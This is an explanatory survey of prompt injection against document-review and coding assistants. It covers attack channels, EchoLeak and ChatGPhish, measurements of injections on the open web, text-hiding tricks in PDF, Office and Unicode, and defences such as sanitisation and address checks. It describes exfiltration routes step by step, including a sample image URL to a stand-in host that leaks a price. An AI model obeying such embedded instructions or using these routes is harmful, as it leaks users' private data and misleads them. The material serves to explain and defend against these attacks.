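# Prompt injection in AI-assisted document review and code generation: attack channels and defences

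## How text given to an assistant to read can act as a command

Prompt injection is an attack on software built around large language models, in which the attacker gets the model to follow instructions that neither its developer nor its user gave or wanted. The risk arises wherever an assistant reads text by strangers, which is a large part of both document review and coding. An assistant that reviews documents reads contracts, papers and job applications from people outside the organisation that runs it. A coding agent, which is a language model with tools to read, write and run code, reads software repositories, bug reports and web pages with many contributors. Any of this text may contain a sentence addressed to the assistant, and the assistant may act on it.

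The term "prompt injection" dates from 2022. The programmer Simon Willison (2025) explains in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* that he modelled it on SQL injection, an older attack on databases, because both attacks come from mixing trusted and untrusted content.

### One sequence of tokens

A language model has a single input, called the context window. Before each reply, the application around the model assembles this input as a sequence of tokens, which are words or fragments of words. The sequence usually starts with the system prompt, where the developer sets out the assistant's job and rules, followed by the user's request. If the assistant opens a file or fetches a web page, the application adds that content too. The model predicts each next token from the whole sequence.

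Applications use special markers to show where the system prompt ends, where the user's message begins and which text came from a tool. *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) describes the intended ranking, in which the system prompt outranks the user and the model should treat text from a tool as information, never as a command. OpenAI's *Our approach to the Model Spec* sets out a similar ranking, called the "chain of command", in which each instruction has an authority level and the company instructs the model to settle conflicts accordingly. Such a ranking makes the model less likely to obey a stranger's text but does not rule it out, because the markers are tokens in the same sequence as the text they label and the model itself has to respect them.

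Ye and colleagues also measured how well models distinguish between speakers. They wrapped identical passages of web text in the markers of five different roles and trained a simple classifier on the model's internal activations to tell the roles apart. Because the wording never varied, the classifier could learn only the effect of the markers. They then applied it to a short conversation about gardening with gpt-oss-20b, an open-weight model. Passages of the model's own reasoning scored 85% as "reasoning" under the correct markers and 83% after the researchers removed all markers. When they wrapped the entire conversation in user markers, the same passages still scored 85% as reasoning and only 2% as user text, which shows that the style of the text had more effect than the markers.

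Across 1,000 attempts to make an agent leak data, Ye and colleagues found that the attack succeeded 2% of the time when the classifier measured the least confusion about roles and 70% of the time when it measured the most. This is a correlation, but a separate attack that imitated the model's own reasoning provides better evidence of causation. When the researchers reworded the text to keep its argument but remove the imitated style, the success rate fell from 61% to 10%.

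### Direct and indirect injection

In direct prompt injection, the attacker is the user. NIST (2025), the US standards institute, defines it as a case in which the application appends the main user's instructions to its designer's more trusted ones. For example, a customer might type a message into a shop's chatbot to try to override the shop's rules.

In indirect prompt injection, the attacker needs no access to the assistant. The attacker writes something that the assistant will read while doing someone else's task, and the victim is usually the person who set the task or the organisation that runs the assistant. Most of the danger in document review and coding comes from indirect injection, because the malicious instructions are in the text rather than in the user's request.

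The term "prompt injection" has more than one meaning. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) describes it as instructions placed in external content, which covers only the indirect form. Many people also use the term for jailbreaking, in which a user tries to get a model past the restrictions on its output. Willison treats jailbreaking as a different problem and thinks the confusion does harm, because developers who equate the two tend to conclude that prompt injection is an embarrassment for the model's vendor and not a problem they need to deal with themselves.

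### Why the SQL remedy does not carry over

Programs query databases in a language called SQL. A carelessly written website might look up a customer by pasting the visitor's input straight into an SQL command. A visitor who types a fragment of SQL instead of a name can then alter the command, and perhaps read or change the whole database.

The remedy is a parameterised query, in which the programmer sends the command with a placeholder for the name and sends the name separately. The engine determines the command's structure without using the name, so the name cannot become part of the command, whatever characters it contains.

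Language models have no equivalent of the remedy for SQL injection. David C's *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, published by the UK's National Cyber Security Centre on 8 December 2025, calls the comparison dangerous for this reason. A database engine handles instructions and data differently, but inside a language model there is only ever the "next token". The statement concludes that prompt injection may never be totally mitigated in the way that SQL injection can be. This is a judgement about current models, not a proof about all possible ones, but the reason for it is strong. A database can store a customer's name without interpreting it, whereas an assistant must interpret a contract to review it, and it interprets a request in the contract by the same process as a request from its user.

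The closest equivalent to the database remedy is to protect the markers. An attacker can type a copy of a marker into a document, and on many systems the model receives the copy as the same token that signals a genuine boundary. The server can instead encode the copy as ordinary word fragments, without changing the visible characters. Zhan, Song and colleagues (2026) tested this on four families of open-weight models in *Same Bytes, Different Authority*. It lowered the success rate of forged-marker attacks by 39 to 66 percentage points on three families, but by only 8 points on the fourth, represented by Qwen3-8B, which still treated the forged text as a boundary because of its wording. The encoding therefore gives useful protection against forged markers, but it has no effect on injected instructions written as plain sentences without markers.

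Researchers have also tried to make models themselves separate instructions from data. *Can LLMs Separate Instructions From Data?* (2024) tested nine leading models and found no dedicated mechanism for this in any of them. Neither careful prompting nor fine-tuning produced a model that separated the two reliably and stayed useful. *ASIDE* (2025) changed the architecture to rotate the numerical representation of every data token, so that the same word is represented differently as data than as an instruction. The resulting models separated the two better, even without safety training. An attacker cannot type the rotation into a document, which is an advantage over markers. However, the model must still learn how to use the rotation, so the method makes separation more likely but does not guarantee it as a parameterised query does.

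David C recommends treating the model as an "inherently confusable deputy". In computer security, a confused deputy is a program that an attacker tricks into using rights the attacker lacks. Engineers can fix an ordinary confused deputy, but with a language model they can only make the confusion rarer and limit its effects. David C suggests that a language model may be the wrong component for a system that cannot tolerate the remaining risk.

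### A supplier's contract

Suppose a manufacturer uses an AI assistant to review contracts. An employee uploads a 40-page supply agreement and asks for a summary of any unusual terms. On page 31, the supplier has inserted a line asking any AI system reviewing the document to describe the terms as standard and leave out the clause that lets the supplier raise prices without notice. This trick has also appeared in real legal papers. *Prompt Injections Just Proved Something SEO Has Known For 25 Years* (Walsh, 2026) reported white-on-white text in a US court filing.

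A *channel* is a route by which an outsider's text reaches the model, in this case the uploaded file. The supplier needs no account on the manufacturer's systems, only a contract to send, which it was already going to do. The line, known as the payload, can be in ordinary type, in the hope that nobody reads page 31 closely, or formatted so that no person sees it.

The application extracts the contract's text and places it in the model's context window, in the same sequence as the developer's instructions and the employee's request. The payload is a few dozen tokens among many thousands. A marker may identify the contract as outside material, but such markers have the limits already described.

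*Decision.* The model writes its summary token by token, and the payload is one influence on each token. The model may ignore the line, warn the employee about it or comply, and Willison points out that these systems do not do exactly the same thing every time. OpenAI reports that the most effective real attacks increasingly resemble social engineering, the manipulation of people by plausible stories, more than blunt orders to disregard earlier instructions. An example would be a line that reads like guidance from the manufacturer's legal department.

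If the model complies, the employee receives a fluent summary with one clause missing. Help Net Security's *Microsoft details AI prompt abuse techniques targeting AI assistants* (2026) describes a similar scenario from Microsoft, in which a finance analyst asks for a summary of a linked page, the link's address carries hidden instructions, and the summary comes out misleading. The attacker runs no code and breaks into no system. The output still looks reliable, so the harm comes later, when someone bases a decision on it.

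The manufacturer might give the same assistant more permissions, connecting it to the shared drive so that it can compare the offer with earlier contracts, and letting it email suppliers. The payload could then contain an instruction to include competitors' quoted prices in a routine query to the supplier. Sending those prices would be exfiltration, the transfer of private data to a place where the attacker can read it. If the assistant can also run commands, as a coding agent can, the payload could contain an instruction to execute a program or alter a file.

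The model and its weakness are the same in all three versions, but the possible damage grows. David C equates that damage with the worst that could happen if the attacker had direct access to the assistant's tools. In discussing direct injection, NIST mentions designing systems on the assumption that a model with access to sensitive data may leak it. That approach suits this case equally well.

Most cases can therefore be classified by who can write the text, whose assistant reads it, and what that assistant may do. In *Who Is Prompt-Injecting Coding Agents?*, Nakibly and Babo (2026) apply the first two criteria to GitHub, the largest site for sharing code. A project's maintainers write its README (the introductory file) and visitors' agents read it, so an attack there would typically harm a visitor. Anyone with an account can file an issue (a bug report or request) and the maintainers' agents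 read it, so the typical victim is the project.

Nakibly and Babo define an attack by its victim, not its wording. A project that tells its own agent to skip an issue is configuring it, but an outsider who tells the same agent to skip a security check is attacking it. Likewise, if the manufacturer in the contract example had put a note in its own template telling its assistant to treat a certain clause as standard, the note would be an ordinary instruction.

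### The lethal trifecta

The most widely used rule of thumb about permissions comes from Willison, who argued in June 2025 that an agent is open to data theft when it combines access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and the ability to communicate outward. He calls this combination the lethal trifecta. The contract assistant with a shared drive and email meets all three conditions, because the drive holds private data, the supplier wrote the untrusted content, and the assistant can send data out by email.

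Removing any one part of the trifecta prevents the theft, even if the model obeys the payload completely. According to Willison, vendors who fixed reported attacks on their products usually did so by blocking the route by which data could leave. This is difficult because email is only the most obvious route. An assistant that can load an image from a web address, or show the user a link to click, can put stolen data into the address. Users also assemble the trifecta without noticing when they connect tools from different sources, and a single tool can supply all of it. Willison's example is a GitHub connector that could read public issues, read private repositories and publish proposed changes.

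The trifecta describes only data theft. The first version of the contract assistant cannot send anything out, but it still produces the biased summary. An agent that can delete files can also do damage without an outward connection.

### Attack success rate

Researchers usually report the strength of an attack or defence as an attack success rate, which is the share of attack attempts or attacked scenarios in which the assistant does what the attacker wanted. If an agent reads 200 poisoned documents and obeys 30 of them, the rate is 15%.

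Tests define a successful attack differently. As Zhan and colleagues explain, the benchmark InjecAgent scores whether the agent calls the attacker's tool after reading a poisoned response, whereas AgentDojo runs a complete multi-step task and checks whether the agent achieved the injected goal. An agent that makes the attacker's first call but fails at a later step could count as a success on InjecAgent and a failure on AgentDojo, so success rates from the two benchmarks are not directly comparable.

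The success rate also depends on the attack as well as the model. Ye and colleagues asked agents to summarise a web page that contained an injection, and counted a success only when the agent uploaded a secret file to a remote server. Ordinary injections succeeded 0 to 2% of the time on every model but one, where the rate was 26%. Adding forged reasoning to the same command raised the rates to between 56 and 70%. A low rate is therefore hard to interpret without knowing how hard the attackers tried, whether they had one attempt or many, and whether they designed the attack against the particular defence under test (an adaptive attack). Success rates also don't measure how often a company will encounter attacks.

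### Channels and defences

*Prompt Injection Attacks on Agentic Coding Assistants* (Maloyan and Namiot, 2026) sorts attacks on coding agents partly by how the text arrives, with separate groups for repositories, documentation, web content and the protocols that connect tools. In document review, attacks can also arrive in the files that people submit for judgement. Defences differ mainly in where they intervene. Sanitisation and input filters act before the model reads the text, training influences what the model decides to do, and a sandbox limits the effect of a wrong decision.

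| | Type | How it works |
|---|---|---|
| Channel | Web pages and links | The assistant fetches a page, or receives a link with text in its address |
| Channel | Documents | A user or an outside party submits a contract, paper, résumé or essay |
| Channel | Repository files | A coding agent reads code comments, documentation, or instruction files that it loads as guidance from the project's owners |
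| Channel | Metadata | An agent reads issue titles, descriptions of proposed changes, or comments |
| Defence | Sanitisation | The application removes or rewrites parts of the input, whatever they say |
| Defence | Input filter | A program or a second model judges whether the input contains an injection, and blocks or flags it |
| Defence | Trained resistance | The developer trains the model not to obey instructions in the content it reads |
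| Defence | Sandbox | The system enforces limits on the files, network addresses and secrets that the agent's commands can reach |

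## Web pages and links (from 2022)

On 11 September 2022, Riley Goodside published several examples in which he asked GPT-3, OpenAI's language model at the time, to translate a passage into French. The passage contained an instruction to ignore the translation request and output a mocking phrase, and GPT-3 output the phrase. The next day Willison (2022), in *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3*, proposed the name "prompt injection" and explained why the problem mattered. Developers were already building products on GPT-3 by joining their own instructions and a customer's text into one string, so anyone who supplied the text could also supply instructions.

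Days later, on 15 September, a recruitment startup released a Twitter bot that used GPT-3 to reply to posts about remote work. Users publicly got it to reveal its original instructions, and one got it to threaten to overthrow the president.

Goodside immediately tried to prevent the attack by rewording the instructions. He warned GPT-3 that the text might contain directions meant to trick it, and told it to keep translating regardless. GPT-3 still followed the injected instruction. He then put the text inside quotation marks in JSON, a structured data format, to mark where it began and ended. This time GPT-3 translated the injected instruction instead of following it, but Brian Mastenbrook soon found an attack that worked despite the quotation marks.

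Willison hoped for an interface with separate slots for instructions and data, like a parameterised SQL query. OpenAI already had a model with separate slots, but injections in its data slot still worked. By April 2023, he thought such a separation was extremely difficult, if not impossible, with the language models of the day. He had already written in *I don’t know how to solve prompt injection* (Willison, 2022), four days after naming the attack, that he knew how to beat SQL injection but had "no idea how to reliably beat prompt injection".

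### Instructions on a page that the assistant retrieves

In these early attacks, the attacker wrote to the model directly. *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023) showed that once assistants could look things up, an attacker could instead put instructions in a page that the assistant might retrieve. The paper introduced the term "indirect prompt injection" for this.

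Greshake and colleagues' cases included the Bing Chat sidebar in Microsoft's Edge browser, which could read and summarise the page the user had open. Instructions on the page affected the model even when the user could not see them. The researchers noted that attackers could reach more people by using search-engine optimisation to make their pages rank higher.

"Not What You've Signed Up For" (Greshake et al., 2023) compares reading an untrusted page to running a stranger's program. The attacker has an advantage with a page, because a payload might only need to state a goal, whereas a program has to spell out every step. In the paper's tests, the model sometimes ran further searches to find evidence for a claim that the payload had asked it to support. The harms described include false summaries, links to scam sites, theft of personal data, and a worm that spreads when an email assistant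 reads a payload and sends it on to other people.

Greshake and colleagues demonstrated attacks on Bing's chat, code-completion tools and test applications they built with GPT-4. Their demonstrations were qualitative, so they showed that the attacks could work but not how often.

### How a link brings text in and carries data out

When an assistant opens a link, it reads the page into its context window, including any text an attacker has put there. The page may contain the full payload, or a short one that sends the assistant to a longer one elsewhere. The link's address can also contain the payload. Some assistants accept links that fill in the user's question in advance, so a person who follows such a link submits a prompt that somebody else wrote.

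Links can also leak data. A web address can include extra text after the page name, which the browser sends to the server with the rest of the address. According to OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026), websites commonly record the addresses that visitors request. If an attacker gets an assistant to put private data in an address on the attacker's server, and something loads that address, the data appears in the attacker's logs.

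Suppose that the manufacturer's contract assistant reads a supplier's web page, and that a payload on the page asks for an image at the end of the summary. The payload specifies that the image's address must include the lowest price that a competitor has quoted. The assistant finds the price on the shared drive and writes this address into its answer:

`https://supplier.example/logo.png?ref=41-per-unit`

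(Internet standards reserve the ending ".example" for illustrations, so the address leads nowhere.) To display the image, the chat window requests it from the supplier's server, which records "41-per-unit". The request itself contains the price, so the supplier receives it even if the server has no logo to send back.

Assistants usually write links and images in Markdown, which uses punctuation marks to indicate formatting, and the chat application converts it into what the user sees. An image sends the data out as soon as the application displays the answer, while a link does so only if the user clicks. An agent that can browse may also load the address itself in the background. Coding agents can also send data out through the commands they run, so they need network limits as well.

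Developers cannot ban all links that contain information about the user, because many of them are useful. A help page from OpenAI gives the example of a link that includes the user's city and leads to a car-search site. The link helps the user find a car but also reveals to the site where they live.

### Blocking images and approving domains

The most direct defence is for the application to block images from other sites. This stops the automatic leak but also blocks legitimate pictures and charts, and a link can still leak data when the user clicks it. The application can also remove links from the assistant's answers, provided that its filter detects every way a link can be written.

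A less drastic defence is an allow-list, a list of domains from which the application may load content. A website can have the browser enforce this list by sending a set of rules, called a Content Security Policy, with its pages. In the example above, the browser would not contact the supplier's server unless the list included it.

OpenAI gives two reasons why a list of trusted sites is not enough. Many legitimate sites offer redirects, which forward a visitor to another address, so a request can start on an approved domain and end on the attacker's server. A strict list also produces frequent false alarms about harmless sites, and users learn to click through the warnings.

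### EchoLeak

An attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, the assistant in Microsoft's office software, got past both a link filter and an allow-list. Researchers at Aim Security discovered the attack, named it EchoLeak and reported it to Microsoft in January 2025. It is listed in the public catalogue of software vulnerabilities as CVE-2025-32711. Reddy and Gujral (2025) reconstructed the attack in *EchoLeak* from Aim's published account.

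The attacker started by sending an ordinary-looking email to an employee. Copilot searches a user's emails and files when it answers a question, so it could later retrieve the attacker's email together with confidential material. The instructions in the email resembled a normal request to the human recipient, and Microsoft's classifier for detecting injections missed them. The attacker also instructed Copilot not to mention the email in its answer, so the employee would not learn where the answer's odd contents came from.

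The payload instructed Copilot to put sensitive details into the address of a link. Copilot's output filter removed external links written in the usual Markdown notation, but not those in a second notation that places the address on a separate line. The employee still had to click the link, so the researchers replaced it with an image, which the chat window would try to load automatically.

Microsoft's Content Security Policy blocked the request because the attacker's domain was not on the allow-list. The list did include a Microsoft Teams service that fetches previews of other web addresses, so the researchers sent the request through it. The employee's browser contacted only an approved Microsoft domain, and the Teams service then passed the data to the attacker's server.

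Aim called the attack "zero-click" because the employee did not have to open a link or an attachment. The employee did have to ask Copilot a question that led it to retrieve the email. SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration* reports a severity score of 9.3 out of 10. Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers in May 2025, a month before the public disclosure, and said that nobody had exploited it.

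Reddy and Gujral describe EchoLeak as the first known prompt injection that could steal data from an AI product in commercial use. Willison (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, describes it as an extended variant of link attacks that researchers had already found in a dozen products. Willison's description of the leak itself seems more accurate. EchoLeak stands out for the number of safeguards it overcame in one product. It is "real-world" in that it affected a real product, though no one is known to have lost data.

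Microsoft later began to strip images and links in the second notation from incoming external content, according to Reddy and Gujral. It also reportedly let customers exclude external messages from Copilot's context in some situations. Excluding them blocks an attacker's email, but Copilot then cannot use a genuine supplier's email either. The allow-list has a more general weakness, because approving a domain approves every service on it, including any that forwards requests elsewhere.

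### Checking the exact address

In January 2026 OpenAI described a defence that checks the whole address, not just the domain. When ChatGPT or one of OpenAI's agents is about to load an address automatically, the system looks for that exact address in an index built by OpenAI's crawler, a program that finds and records public web pages. The crawler has no access to users' conversations. An address in its index was therefore already public independently of the conversation, and is unlikely to contain that user's private data.

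In the supplier example, the address of the plain logo might be in the index, but the version that ends in a competitor's price would not be. The system would then either have the agent try another site or warn the user. OpenAI calls the mechanism Safe Url and also applies it to page visits in its Atlas browser and to searches by its Deep Research agent. The warning can show the information that the address would transmit, which is more informative than the name of an unfamiliar site.

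This handles redirects better than an allow-list does, because it no longer accepts an address just because the domain is trusted. Some false alarms remain. Some websites ask OpenAI not to catalogue them, and OpenAI's help page explains that ChatGPT then asks users to confirm every link to those sites. Those users may fall back into the habit of confirming links without checking them.

A small leak also remains possible in principle. If an attacker publishes one page for "yes" and another for "no", both addresses could be in the index, and an agent's choice between them would reveal the answer to one yes-or-no question. OpenAI claims only that a public address is "much less likely" to contain private data. It also limits the guarantee to quiet leaks through the address, and does not promise that a page's content is trustworthy or free of harmful instructions.

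### ChatGPhish

*ChatGPhish*, published by the security company Permiso in May 2026, describes an attack that relied on that kind of content. Permiso added instructions to a web page, then used a menu option in the Firefox browser to ask ChatGPT to summarise it. ChatGPT wrote a genuine summary, followed by a false notice that someone had added a new device to the user's account. The notice included a link chosen by the attacker.

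The problem arose partly because the model followed the page's formatting instructions, and partly because ChatGPT's web interface turned Markdown from the page into live links and images without labelling them as third-party content. Permiso found the same behaviour with a README on GitHub and with an ordinary web page on its own server. Firefox only passed the page to ChatGPT and did not cause the problem.

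In another version, the false notice contained a QR code. Scanning it moves the user from the computer to a phone, where the computer's protections no longer apply. The user cannot hover over a link to see its destination, and a password manager on the computer cannot detect that the domain is wrong. Permiso also used a remote image to track users. When the answer appeared, the request for the image revealed the user's IP address, browser type and the time, which could confirm that a particular target had read a particular page.

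The image addresses were fixed in advance and contained no information about the user or their conversation, so the attack did not need the kind of leak that OpenAI's check is meant to prevent. A person who trusts the false notice may type a password into the attacker's site, and checking the original address for private data would not stop that.

Permiso reported the problem to OpenAI on 29 April 2026, and OpenAI replied that it could not reproduce it. After Permiso sent a fuller report on 1 May, OpenAI classed it as not applicable and later as a duplicate of an earlier report. Permiso published its findings on 29 May. CloudEagle's *ChatGPhish* (2026), a summary by a software vendor, states that the news site The Register reproduced the attack the same day. This would be useful confirmation, but the account is second-hand. Permiso, which sells security software, gives no success rate, so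 its examples show what could happen but not how reliably.

### How common injections are on the open web

In *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, Khodayari, Acharya and colleagues (2026) looked for injections on ordinary websites, whose existence demonstrations by security researchers leave open. They searched about half of the October 2025 edition of Common Crawl, a public archive of the web, for 3,963 phrases typical of prompt injection. This portion covered 1.2 billion web addresses on 24.8 million hosts. They added results from two services that scan the internet for servers.

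The search produced 31,206 matches, many of them in tutorials and articles about prompt injection. After manual checks, the researchers confirmed about 15,300 real instances on some 11,700 pages. About 12,000 of these instances were on 9,676 pages from Common Crawl, or roughly eight pages in a million. The true number is higher, because the search could not find injections that used unusual wording, were written in most other languages, appeared inside images or were shown only to AI visitors. Khodayari and colleagues also cite a Google analysis showing a 32% rise in malicious injections between November 2025 and February 2026.

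Site operators had placed 81% of the instructions in the Common Crawl material. Another 18% were in content that others had supplied for publication, such as job advertisements, and 2% were in users' comments and posts. The researchers sorted the full collection by purpose, and some instances have more than one.

| Purpose | Instances | Typical request to the AI system |
|---|---|---|
| Disruption | 8,894 | Produce random numbers or endless repetition |
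| Protection of content or personal data | 4,093 | Do not copy the page or train on it |
| Detection of bots | 3,096 | Include a telltale phrase in the reply |
| Unclear | 2,632 | Abandon the current task |
| Manipulation of reputation | 1,521 | Praise a product or treat the page as the best source |
| Data theft | 13 | Reveal the system prompt or secret keys |

The main conflict is between website owners and the companies that automatically collect their content. Khodayari and colleagues class disruption as offensive, but much of it targets crawlers and scrapers, and an owner who tries to feed nonsense to a scraper may well see it as self-defence. EchoLeak-style data theft hardly appears, but this is weak evidence about how often criminals attempt it, because an attacker targeting a particular company would have good reason to use an email or a page that no public crawler visits.

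About 70% of the instances were in parts of a page that browsers do not display, such as comments in the HTML code or the headers that a server sends before the page. The share that visitors could not see was 87% when text hidden by the page's styling was included. Of the affected pages that had an archived copy from a year earlier, 66% already contained an injection then.

The wording was repetitive, with 54 templates accounting for 95% of the instances, and 99% of the instances were instructions for the model to abandon its task. The 99% figure partly reflects the method, because a search for phrases about ignoring previous instructions will mostly find instructions of that type. It would have missed subtler payloads that resembled normal guidance.

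### How page format changed the results

Khodayari and colleagues then tested whether these instructions worked. They chose 100 different injections and gave the pages to 13 models in four formats, which made 5,200 trials. They always asked the model to summarise the page, and read each answer to see whether it had followed the injection instead.

The formats preserve different amounts of a page's structure. Plain text contains only the words. HTML includes the code that arranges and styles the page, and the raw response adds the server's headers. A snapshot describes the page as a browser would display it, including which parts are visible and which are buttons or links.

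| Format | Model followed the injection | Model failed to produce a usable answer |
|---|---|---|
| Plain text | 3.9% | 0.7% |
| Snapshot | 1.1% | 3.5% |
| HTML | 1.1% | 20.3% |
| Raw response | 0.2% | 25.8% |

The researchers attribute the difference to the clues that each format preserves. HTML shows that an instruction is inside a comment or an invisible element, while in plain text the same instruction looks like any other sentence. The low figures for HTML and the raw response are partly misleading, because those formats were often too long for a model's context window and the model failed before it could follow the injected instruction. The snapshot is a better comparison with plain text because few trials failed in either format, and it supports the researchers' explanation.

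Some of the difference may arise because the formats don't all pass on the same injections. An instruction in a server header, for example, reaches the model only in the raw response. A low rate in one format may therefore mean that the payload never reached some models.

Small models, with up to 8 billion parameters, followed the injection in 8.0% of plain-text trials, compared with 2.4% to 3.4% for the other groups. Across all formats, the rate was 4.2% for small models and 0.6% for the two closed models, one of which was OpenAI's GPT-5.4. The closed models also pointed out the injection most often, in 25% of trials. In six trials, a model identified the malicious instruction but still followed it, for instance by switching to German.

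These rates are for injections that website owners have written, most of them crude and none tuned to the model under test. The much higher success of the forged reasoning in the tests by Ye and colleagues suggests that a determined attacker could achieve more. Khodayari and colleagues tested no agents with tools, so they could not measure how often a model that followed a page's instructions would then send data or change a file.

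## Text that people cannot see, and its removal (from 2024)

A person who opens a file sees what a browser, PDF viewer or office program draws on the screen, while a language model usually receives text that another program has extracted from the file. An attacker can exploit this difference by adding text that reaches the model but does not appear on the screen. Most of the web injections that Khodayari and colleagues found were hidden from visitors in this way, and attackers can also hide text in PDFs, Office files and even plain text.

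In *PhantomLint*, Murray (2025) traces the idea of hidden text to March 2023, when the researcher Mark Riedl put white text on his web page and caused Microsoft's Bing assistant to return false information about him. Later that year, job applicants were hiding text in their CVs. In July 2025, Lin found white or microscopic instructions in 18 research preprints (*Hidden Prompts in Manuscripts Exploit AI-Assisted Peer Review*, 2026).

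### One file, two documents

A PDF page is a series of drawing commands that refer to characters by number. The font determines which shape the viewer draws for each number, while a separate table maps the number to a letter for extraction software. Liu and Ming (2026), in *What Users See Is Not What Models Read*, show that an attacker can make the displayed and extracted text differ. In one of their examples, the viewer draws an "R" and the extractor outputs an "A". In another, the page shows "SAFE", but a label intended for accessibility software causes some extractors to output "FRAUD". The PDF standard does not require the displayed and extracted text to match, because it predates language models and keeps the two separate to support searching, copying and accessibility.

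Liu and Ming found 25 such differences and tested them on 16 PDF-processing systems and seven commercial language-model services. Each service was exposed to between 12 and 21 of them.

Office files leave even more room for the extracted text to differ from what the user sees. A Word, Excel or PowerPoint file is a ZIP archive of linked XML files, with text in some of them and rules for displaying it in others. An extractor must choose which parts to read, whether to apply the display rules and in what order to output the pieces. In *When File Ingestion Misleads Language Models*, Li (2026) tested ten widely used extractors, and the output of every one differed from what Office displays. Li identified 19 places from which at least one extractor passed on text the user would not see, and 12 where at least one dropped text the user would see. For example, two of the Word extractors skip headers,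 footers and footnotes, so a safety limit printed in a footer never reaches the model.

Developers could avoid many of these differences by giving the model an image of each page. Li estimates that this costs roughly a hundred times as much as extracting the text. Extracted text is also easier to search and divide into passages, so most applications use it.

### Ways of hiding text

The simplest way to hide text is to set it in the background colour or in tiny type. The PDF format also has a drawing mode that gives letters no outline or fill, so a reader can't see them on the page but can still select them. An author can also put text on a layer that is switched off, place it beyond the edge of the page, or cover it with an image.

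Word can hide text, Excel can hide rows and sheets, and PowerPoint can hide slides. Slides can also have speaker notes, and pictures can have alternative text, which describes them for people who cannot see them. A file's properties, such as its title and keywords, are in a separate part of the file and reach the model only if the extractor reads that part.

An attacker can hide text on a web page by putting it in an HTML comment, which browsers never display, or by using styling rules (CSS) to hide the element that contains it. An attacker can also put text in the page's metadata. Khodayari and colleagues counted 221 injections in metadata tags, many of them in the fields that social and messaging sites use for link previews, so the text can spread to systems that never open the page.

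Unicode, the standard that assigns a number to every character, includes characters with no visible form. Its tag characters duplicate the basic Latin letters, digits and punctuation, so a run of them can spell an English sentence that nobody sees. Zero-width characters take up no space. An attacker can put them inside a word to make a search for it fail, or arrange them in patterns that encode a message. Direction controls, meant for text that mixes languages such as English and Arabic, can make a line appear in a different order from the one the model receives. Unlike white type or a hidden layer, these characters are part of the text itself, so they usually remain when someone copies the text or converts the file.

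Invisible Unicode seems to be a rare method of attack, despite the attention researchers have paid to it. Nakibly and Babo examined the READMEs of two million GitHub projects and found invisible characters in 1,777 of them. Almost all had an ordinary purpose, such as forming emoji or writing Persian. Only one README contained hidden instructions for an agent, which told it to praise a particular contributor's work.

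An image can contain text that appears only after resizing. Many applications shrink large images before passing them to a model, calculating each new pixel from a few of the old ones. An attacker who knows the method can adjust those old pixels so that letters appear in the smaller copy, while the original, which the user sees, still looks like an ordinary picture.

The table shows how common software treats the other methods, according to the tests by Murray and Li and the survey by Nakibly and Babo.

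| Hidden text | What a person sees | What reaches the model |
|---|---|---|
| White, tiny or unpainted text in a PDF | Nothing, or a thin line | Extractors pass it on unless they check colour, size and drawing mode |
| PDF layer that is switched off | Nothing | The extractors pdftotext and PyMuPDF skip it, but ChatGPT read it |
| PDF text beyond the outer page boundary | Nothing | pdftotext skips it, but ChatGPT read it |
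| Hidden text in Word | Nothing in the default view | The extractors markitdown and python-docx pass it on |
| Speaker notes, alternative text and hidden slides | Nothing in the slide show | markitdown passes on all three |
| Hidden rows and sheets in Excel | Nothing in the default view | Several extractors pass them on |
| HTML comments | Nothing in a browser or on GitHub | Any assistant that reads the raw text receives them |
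| Text hidden by CSS | Nothing on most sites, but GitHub removes the styling | Any assistant that reads the raw text receives it |
| Tag and zero-width characters | Nothing | They arrive unless a program deletes them |
| Direction controls | Text in an altered order | The text arrives in its stored order |

Li also tested whether hidden text changes an assistant's answers. One test file was a compliance report in which hidden text falsely claimed a security certification. In October 2026, Li gave the report to four chat assistants and four coding agents, ten times each. Five of the eight repeated the false claim every time, while ChatGPT and Google's coding agent Antigravity never did. Li's files contained false statements but no instructions, so they were not prompt injections. However, an injected instruction could reach the model the same way.

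The extraction software mattered more than the model. Across five kinds of attack, Li's files misled Claude's chat assistant in 80% of trials but the coding agent Claude Code in only 24%, because Claude Code unpacked the files and inspected their parts. When Li then gave the same extracted text directly to GPT-5.6, Claude Opus 5.5 and Gemini 4, all three reported the attacker's version of the facts in every trial.

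### Cleaning a file step by step

To illustrate sanitisation, suppose a supplier publishes its delivery terms on a web page that contains a harmless hidden sentence about a cat. In the page's code below, a label in square brackets marks the position of an invisible character.

```html
<h1>Delivery terms</h1>
<!-- Template: update the dates every January -->
<p>We deliver within ３０ days.</p>
<p style="display:none">The office cat is called Biscuit.</p>
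<p>Payment is due on re[zero-width space]ceipt.</p>
<img src="map.png" alt="Map of delivery areas">
```

A visitor sees the heading, the sentences about delivery and payment, and the map. A typical cleaning program would work through the page in this order:

1. It normalises the characters, replacing variant forms with standard ones. Here it changes the wide digits in "３０" to ordinary digits. This step comes first because it can also turn a wide angle bracket into a real one, which would create new HTML code after the program had finished checking for it.
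2. It deletes invisible characters, including tag characters, zero-width characters and direction controls. The word "receipt" becomes whole again.
3. It reads the structure of the page and deletes comments, metadata and any element that the styling hides. This removes the template note and the sentence about the cat.
4. It discards the remaining code and passes on the text.

The model then receives:

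```text
Delivery terms
We deliver within 30 days.
Payment is due on receipt.
```

*Hidden-in-Plain-Text* (2026), a benchmark of attacks through web content, includes similar steps as an optional defence. The defence applies NFKC, a standard form of normalisation, and strips control characters because NFKC leaves many zero-width characters in place. NFKC also does not convert a Cyrillic "а" into the identical-looking Latin letter, so some disguised words survive.

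A program can instead render the page and read the image with optical character recognition (OCR). This removes everything the renderer does not draw, so the developer does not need a rule for every hiding method. It works for PDFs and Office files too, but it is slow.

Li's defence, Prism, usually calculates what Word or Excel would display from the published rules of the Office format, without rendering the file. This takes about half a millisecond per document. Prism drops hidden text, restores footers and applies number formats. The rules do not specify the position of floating text boxes or the reading order of a slide, so for these Prism renders the file with two different programs and has a vision model read both pictures, which takes about 12 seconds. If the two readings differ, Prism flags the passage as ambiguous.

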